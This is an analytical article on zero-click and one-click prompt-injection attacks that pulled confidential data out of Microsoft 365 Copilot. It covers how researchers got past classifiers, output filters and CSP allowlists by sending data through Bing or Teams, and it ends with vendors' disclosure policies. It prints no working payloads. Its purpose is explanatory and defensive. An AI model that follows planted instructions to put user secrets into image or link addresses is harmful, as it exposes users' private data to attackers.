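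The employee did have to use Copilot. According to *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025), the planted email entered the context when the employee later asked a question and Copilot searched the mailbox for material. Fortune (2025) instead describes the assistant as scanning emails in the background.

Microsoft had three safeguards against the attack. The first was a classifier for injected instructions, which the researchers got past by wording the email as an ordinary request to its human reader. The second was a filter that removed outside links from Copilot's replies. It recognised the usual markdown notation but not the one that gives the address on a separate line. The space that Microsoft inserted in the Azure playground would not have blocked that notation either.

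The third safeguard was Copilot's CSP, which blocked images from unknown domains. However, it allowed a Microsoft Teams address that would fetch other URLs on request. The browser sent a request containing the stolen data to Teams, which forwarded it to the attacker's server.

An attacker could have obtained anything Copilot could find for that employee, including internal emails and files. The email also told Copilot not to mention it, so the victim would have seen at most a broken image. Microsoft had started on a fix by April and completed it in May, and Aim Labs published its findings on 11 June. Reddy and Gujral report that Microsoft had no evidence of anyone using the flaw against real victims.

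Reddy and Gujral also call EchoLeak the first known case of prompt injection causing concrete data theft in a production system. This claim is doubtful, since Rehberger had extracted a secret from Bing Chat in 2023, also without a click. Willison, in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, more plausibly describes it as an extended variant of attacks already seen in a dozen products. EchoLeak differed from the Bing Chat attack in its delivery. The attacker could email a chosen victim instead of waiting for someone to open a web page.

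### An image that loaded too early

In the next case, the victim had to click one link. *SearchLeak*, which the security firm Varonis published on 15 June 2026, describes a flaw (CVE-2026-42824) in Copilot's Enterprise Search, which searches a company's own emails, meetings and files. The link led to a genuine Microsoft address and contained a search query, which Copilot treated as instructions to carry out.

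Marking outside text with Spotlighting would probably not have helped, because the attacker's words arrived as if the user had typed them. Varonis had already used the same trick against the consumer version of Copilot, and its researchers were surprised that it still worked in the business version.

This time Microsoft's filter could handle the notation. It put Copilot's reply into a code block so that an image tag would appear as text. But it did so only once the reply was complete, and Copilot displays a reply piece by piece as the model writes it. The browser therefore requested the image before the filter disabled the tag.

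The CSP would still have blocked a direct request to the attacker's server, but it allowed requests to every Bing address. Bing's image search fetches pictures from addresses that users give it, so it passed the data on to the attacker, as Teams had done a year earlier.

In the demonstration, Varonis extracted an email's subject line, which can be enough to break into an account because some services put one-time security codes there. The firm says the attack could also have reached email text, calendar entries and indexed company files. Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers in early June, before Varonis published, according to Daily Security Review's *CVE-2026-42824*. Varonis reports no attacks on real users, but it doesn't say whether anyone looked for them.

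### Bing again

The EchoLeak team became Cato AI Labs after the network security company Cato Networks bought Aim Security. On 3 December 2026, the team published *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026), which presents three more zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot. Each attack began with an unread email that Copilot retrieved while answering an ordinary question, and each sent the data out by a different route.

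One way to leak data, tracked as CVE-2026-124115, used an image. Copilot put confidential information into an image address, the user's browser loaded the image, and Bing forwarded the request to an outside server. Antipov (2026) points out the similarity to SearchLeak in *Письмо даже не нужно открывать*. Cato reported its three findings to Microsoft between 29 July and 20 August, so an attacker could still use Bing as a relay less than three months after the SearchLeak fix.

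Microsoft may have closed the other gaps in SearchLeak and left the relay open, or Cato may have found a different way through Bing. Neither Antipov nor *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (Faisal, 2026) settles which happened. In both cases, Microsoft had missed a close variant of a flaw it had just fixed, which its 2025 account says it tries to prevent.

The other two routes didn't use images on the chat page. In CVE-2026-124132, Copilot created a Word, Excel, PowerPoint or PDF file with a link containing confidential data. Microsoft's servers later processed the file in the background and contacted the link's address. In Cato's tests, this happened one to eight minutes after the conversation ended, even if nobody opened the file. A filter on the chat page can't stop these requests because they come from a server.

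CVE-2026-78501 was a flaw in Copilot's code interpreter, which runs small programs in an isolated environment. Microsoft guarantees in its documentation that no network traffic enters or leaves such environments, but Cato's researchers broke the isolation and sent data straight out. Microsoft had the right rule here but failed to enforce it.

All three attacks could expose confidential material that the user had permission to see. Faisal reports that Microsoft fixed the code interpreter on 17 September, the generated files on 11 November and the Bing image route on 15 November. When Cato published, it knew of no affected customers or real attacks.

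### Every notation and every service

A text filter can prevent image leaks only if it recognises every notation that the page accepts and finishes before the page displays anything. In EchoLeak, Copilot's filter missed at least one notation, and in SearchLeak, the filter finished too late.

A fix has to cover every place where the product displays the model's output. Rehberger found another such place, the HTML page preview in Microsoft 365 Copilot, and reported it in 2025. Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON* explains how the preview could send data out. Microsoft has since patched the flaw, listed as CVE-2026-24299.

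An allowlist avoids the problem of notation, but a service on the list can still pass data to an attacker. Suppose the operator of Mira's assistant at chat.example also permits images from previews.example, which makes thumbnails of other web pages. Planted text could then make the model write an image address at previews.example that contains a second address, the one at collector.example with Mira's name and code. The browser allows the request because previews.example is on the list, and the preview service then requests the collector.example address. The attacker's log shows the service's network address instead of Mira's, but it still includes her code, 4471.

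Security researchers call this server-side request forgery, and Varonis notes that it has been around for more than a decade. An allowlist is therefore only as safe as the least safe service on it. Copilot's list included everything under bing.com. Bing Chat's list had also consisted of Bing domains in 2023, though nobody has reported a relay there. To the team that runs Copilot, these addresses were trustworthy because they belonged to Microsoft. But image searches and link previews routinely fetch addresses that strangers supply, and the people who built those services had no particular reason to think of Copilot. A service that was harmless when it was added to the list can also gain such a function later.

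A relay inside Microsoft also makes the leak harder to notice. Nexo Causal's *ReLeak* (2026) advises investigators to match the outside email with the user's question and the browser's outgoing request. In these attacks, that request went to Bing or Teams, which office computers contact all day.

Varonis recommends sanitizing the output as the page renders it, and checking allowlists for any domain that fetches URLs supplied by users. Checking the allowlists would have addressed the relay in both SearchLeak and EchoLeak. A domain that only returns stored images would be much safer to allow than a whole search engine.

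### Microsoft's defence

Microsoft doesn't claim that any single layer is enough. Besides the filters, it points to controls over what Copilot can read. A company can label sensitive files and stop Copilot from summarising them, which limits the damage if an injection succeeds. Microsoft also relies on the user's consent for some actions, such as sending an email that Copilot in Outlook has drafted. Consent does little against an image leak, because the browser loads the image without the user's approval.

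Microsoft also funds research on prompt injection. More than 800 people took part in its public contest to break defences against these attacks, and it released the resulting collection of over 370,000 prompts. One of its experimental detectors, TaskTracker, examines the model's internal activity instead of its text. Another project, FIDES, uses information-flow control, an established technique that tracks where data came from and restricts where it may go. This could prevent more leaks than a list of image addresses can, because the restriction would also apply when data passes through files and tools.

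The existing layers did make the attacks harder. Aim's researchers told Fortune that they had spent about three months reverse engineering Copilot, whereas Rehberger needed two sentences to attack the Azure playground. The layers may now be giving less protection. According to Antipov, Cato's researchers directed AI agents to write test cases, analyse Copilot's refusals and adjust the next attempts. Attackers can use agents in the same way.

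In all three cases, Microsoft closed the holes before the researchers published, though not always quickly. It made the fixes on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install. The Azure playground fix took 51 days, and the EchoLeak fix took about four months. The fix for the Bing route in ReLeak took between 87 and 109 days, depending on when in the reporting period Cato submitted it.

Faisal quotes Cato's verdict that "too little progress has been made" since EchoLeak. Cato sells AI security products, so it has an interest in saying this. The criticism is a little unfair about the model, because nobody has found a reliable way to make language models distinguish instructions from data. It is much stronger about the relay. Server-side request forgery was a familiar problem long before Copilot existed. EchoLeak had shown in early 2025 that the technique could bypass this same CSP, and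 it worked through Bing in two further attacks.

### When does a leak count as a vulnerability?

Microsoft fixed these flaws because it accepted that they were vulnerabilities, but it doesn't accept every report. Under its published criteria, text that only changes what the model writes gets no severity rating. Prompt injection counts as a vulnerability when it has a security impact, such as the theft of another user's data. Microsoft also excludes extracting a system prompt, the developer's standing instructions to the model.

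The engineer John Russell reported four problems in Copilot, including a prompt injection that revealed the system prompt, and Microsoft rejected all four under its criteria, according to TecnetOne. The decision follows directly from the published rule, at least for the system prompt. The rule is defensible because a system prompt normally contains the developer's text, not the user's, and a developer who puts secrets in it has made a separate mistake.

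*Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents*, by the security firm Checkmarx, describes an attack on Copilot Chat in a development environment. The assistant read an online resource that the attacker controlled, such as an article, and then wrote an image address containing a secret key for an AI service. The image never appeared, but the request for it still reached the researchers' server. Checkmarx reported the attack to MSRC on 15 October 2025, and MSRC closed the report on 4 November without a fix.

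MSRC gave three reasons. The attack required several user actions that were not part of the default setup, it didn't work reliably in different environments, and the product displayed warnings. MSRC also cited "Workplace Trust", the principle that users review and trust the code they choose to run. It probably meant Workspace Trust, a feature of the code editor VS Code that asks whether the user trusts a folder's authors. If so, the product was most likely GitHub Copilot Chat, where GitHub had restricted images in 2024.

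Checkmarx and MSRC disagree partly because they focus on different stages of the attack. Checkmarx calls the leak zero-click because the user doesn't have to do anything more once the assistant has read the attacker's text. MSRC considers what has to happen before that, and Checkmarx concedes that getting the assistant to read the text can be somewhat complex. Microsoft's criteria allow it to consider ease of exploitation.

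Even so, the refusal fits poorly with the rest of Microsoft's record. Its criteria rate the theft of another user's data as Important even when the victim has to click more than once, and they set no limit on the number of actions. Microsoft had also fixed the Azure playground leak, which required the victim to paste in the attacker's text. Warnings might justify a lower rating, but a programmer who lets an assistant read an article has hardly agreed to send its author a secret key. MSRC did pass the finding to the engineers to consider making the behaviour clearer to users, but without committing to stop it.

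Google's assistant Gemini doesn't render images from outside addresses, so the automatic leak didn't work there. Checkmarx reported that Gemini could still leak private data through a link if the user clicked it. Google closed the report after four days, calling the problem infeasible to fix.

Severity ratings can differ even when everyone agrees that a flaw is real. Varonis says that Microsoft rated SearchLeak Critical, its highest severity, although the published criteria reserve that level for attacks that need no action from the victim. Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails, MFA Codes* reports that Microsoft scored it 6.5 out of 10, or medium, because the victim had to click. The US National Vulnerability Database gave it 7.5, assuming that no user action was needed, which doesn't match Varonis' description. TechRadar reported a score of 10. Microsoft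 may well have issued both the Critical label and the 6.5, since they belong to separate scales.

In *Abuse Risks are Often Inherent to Product Features*, Piao, Li and Woods (2025) studied the disclosure policies of 264 AI vendors. They point out that finding and fixing such flaws depends on vendors accepting and rewarding reports. When a vendor rejects a report, the researcher is free to publish while the flaw is still unfixed, as Checkmarx did.
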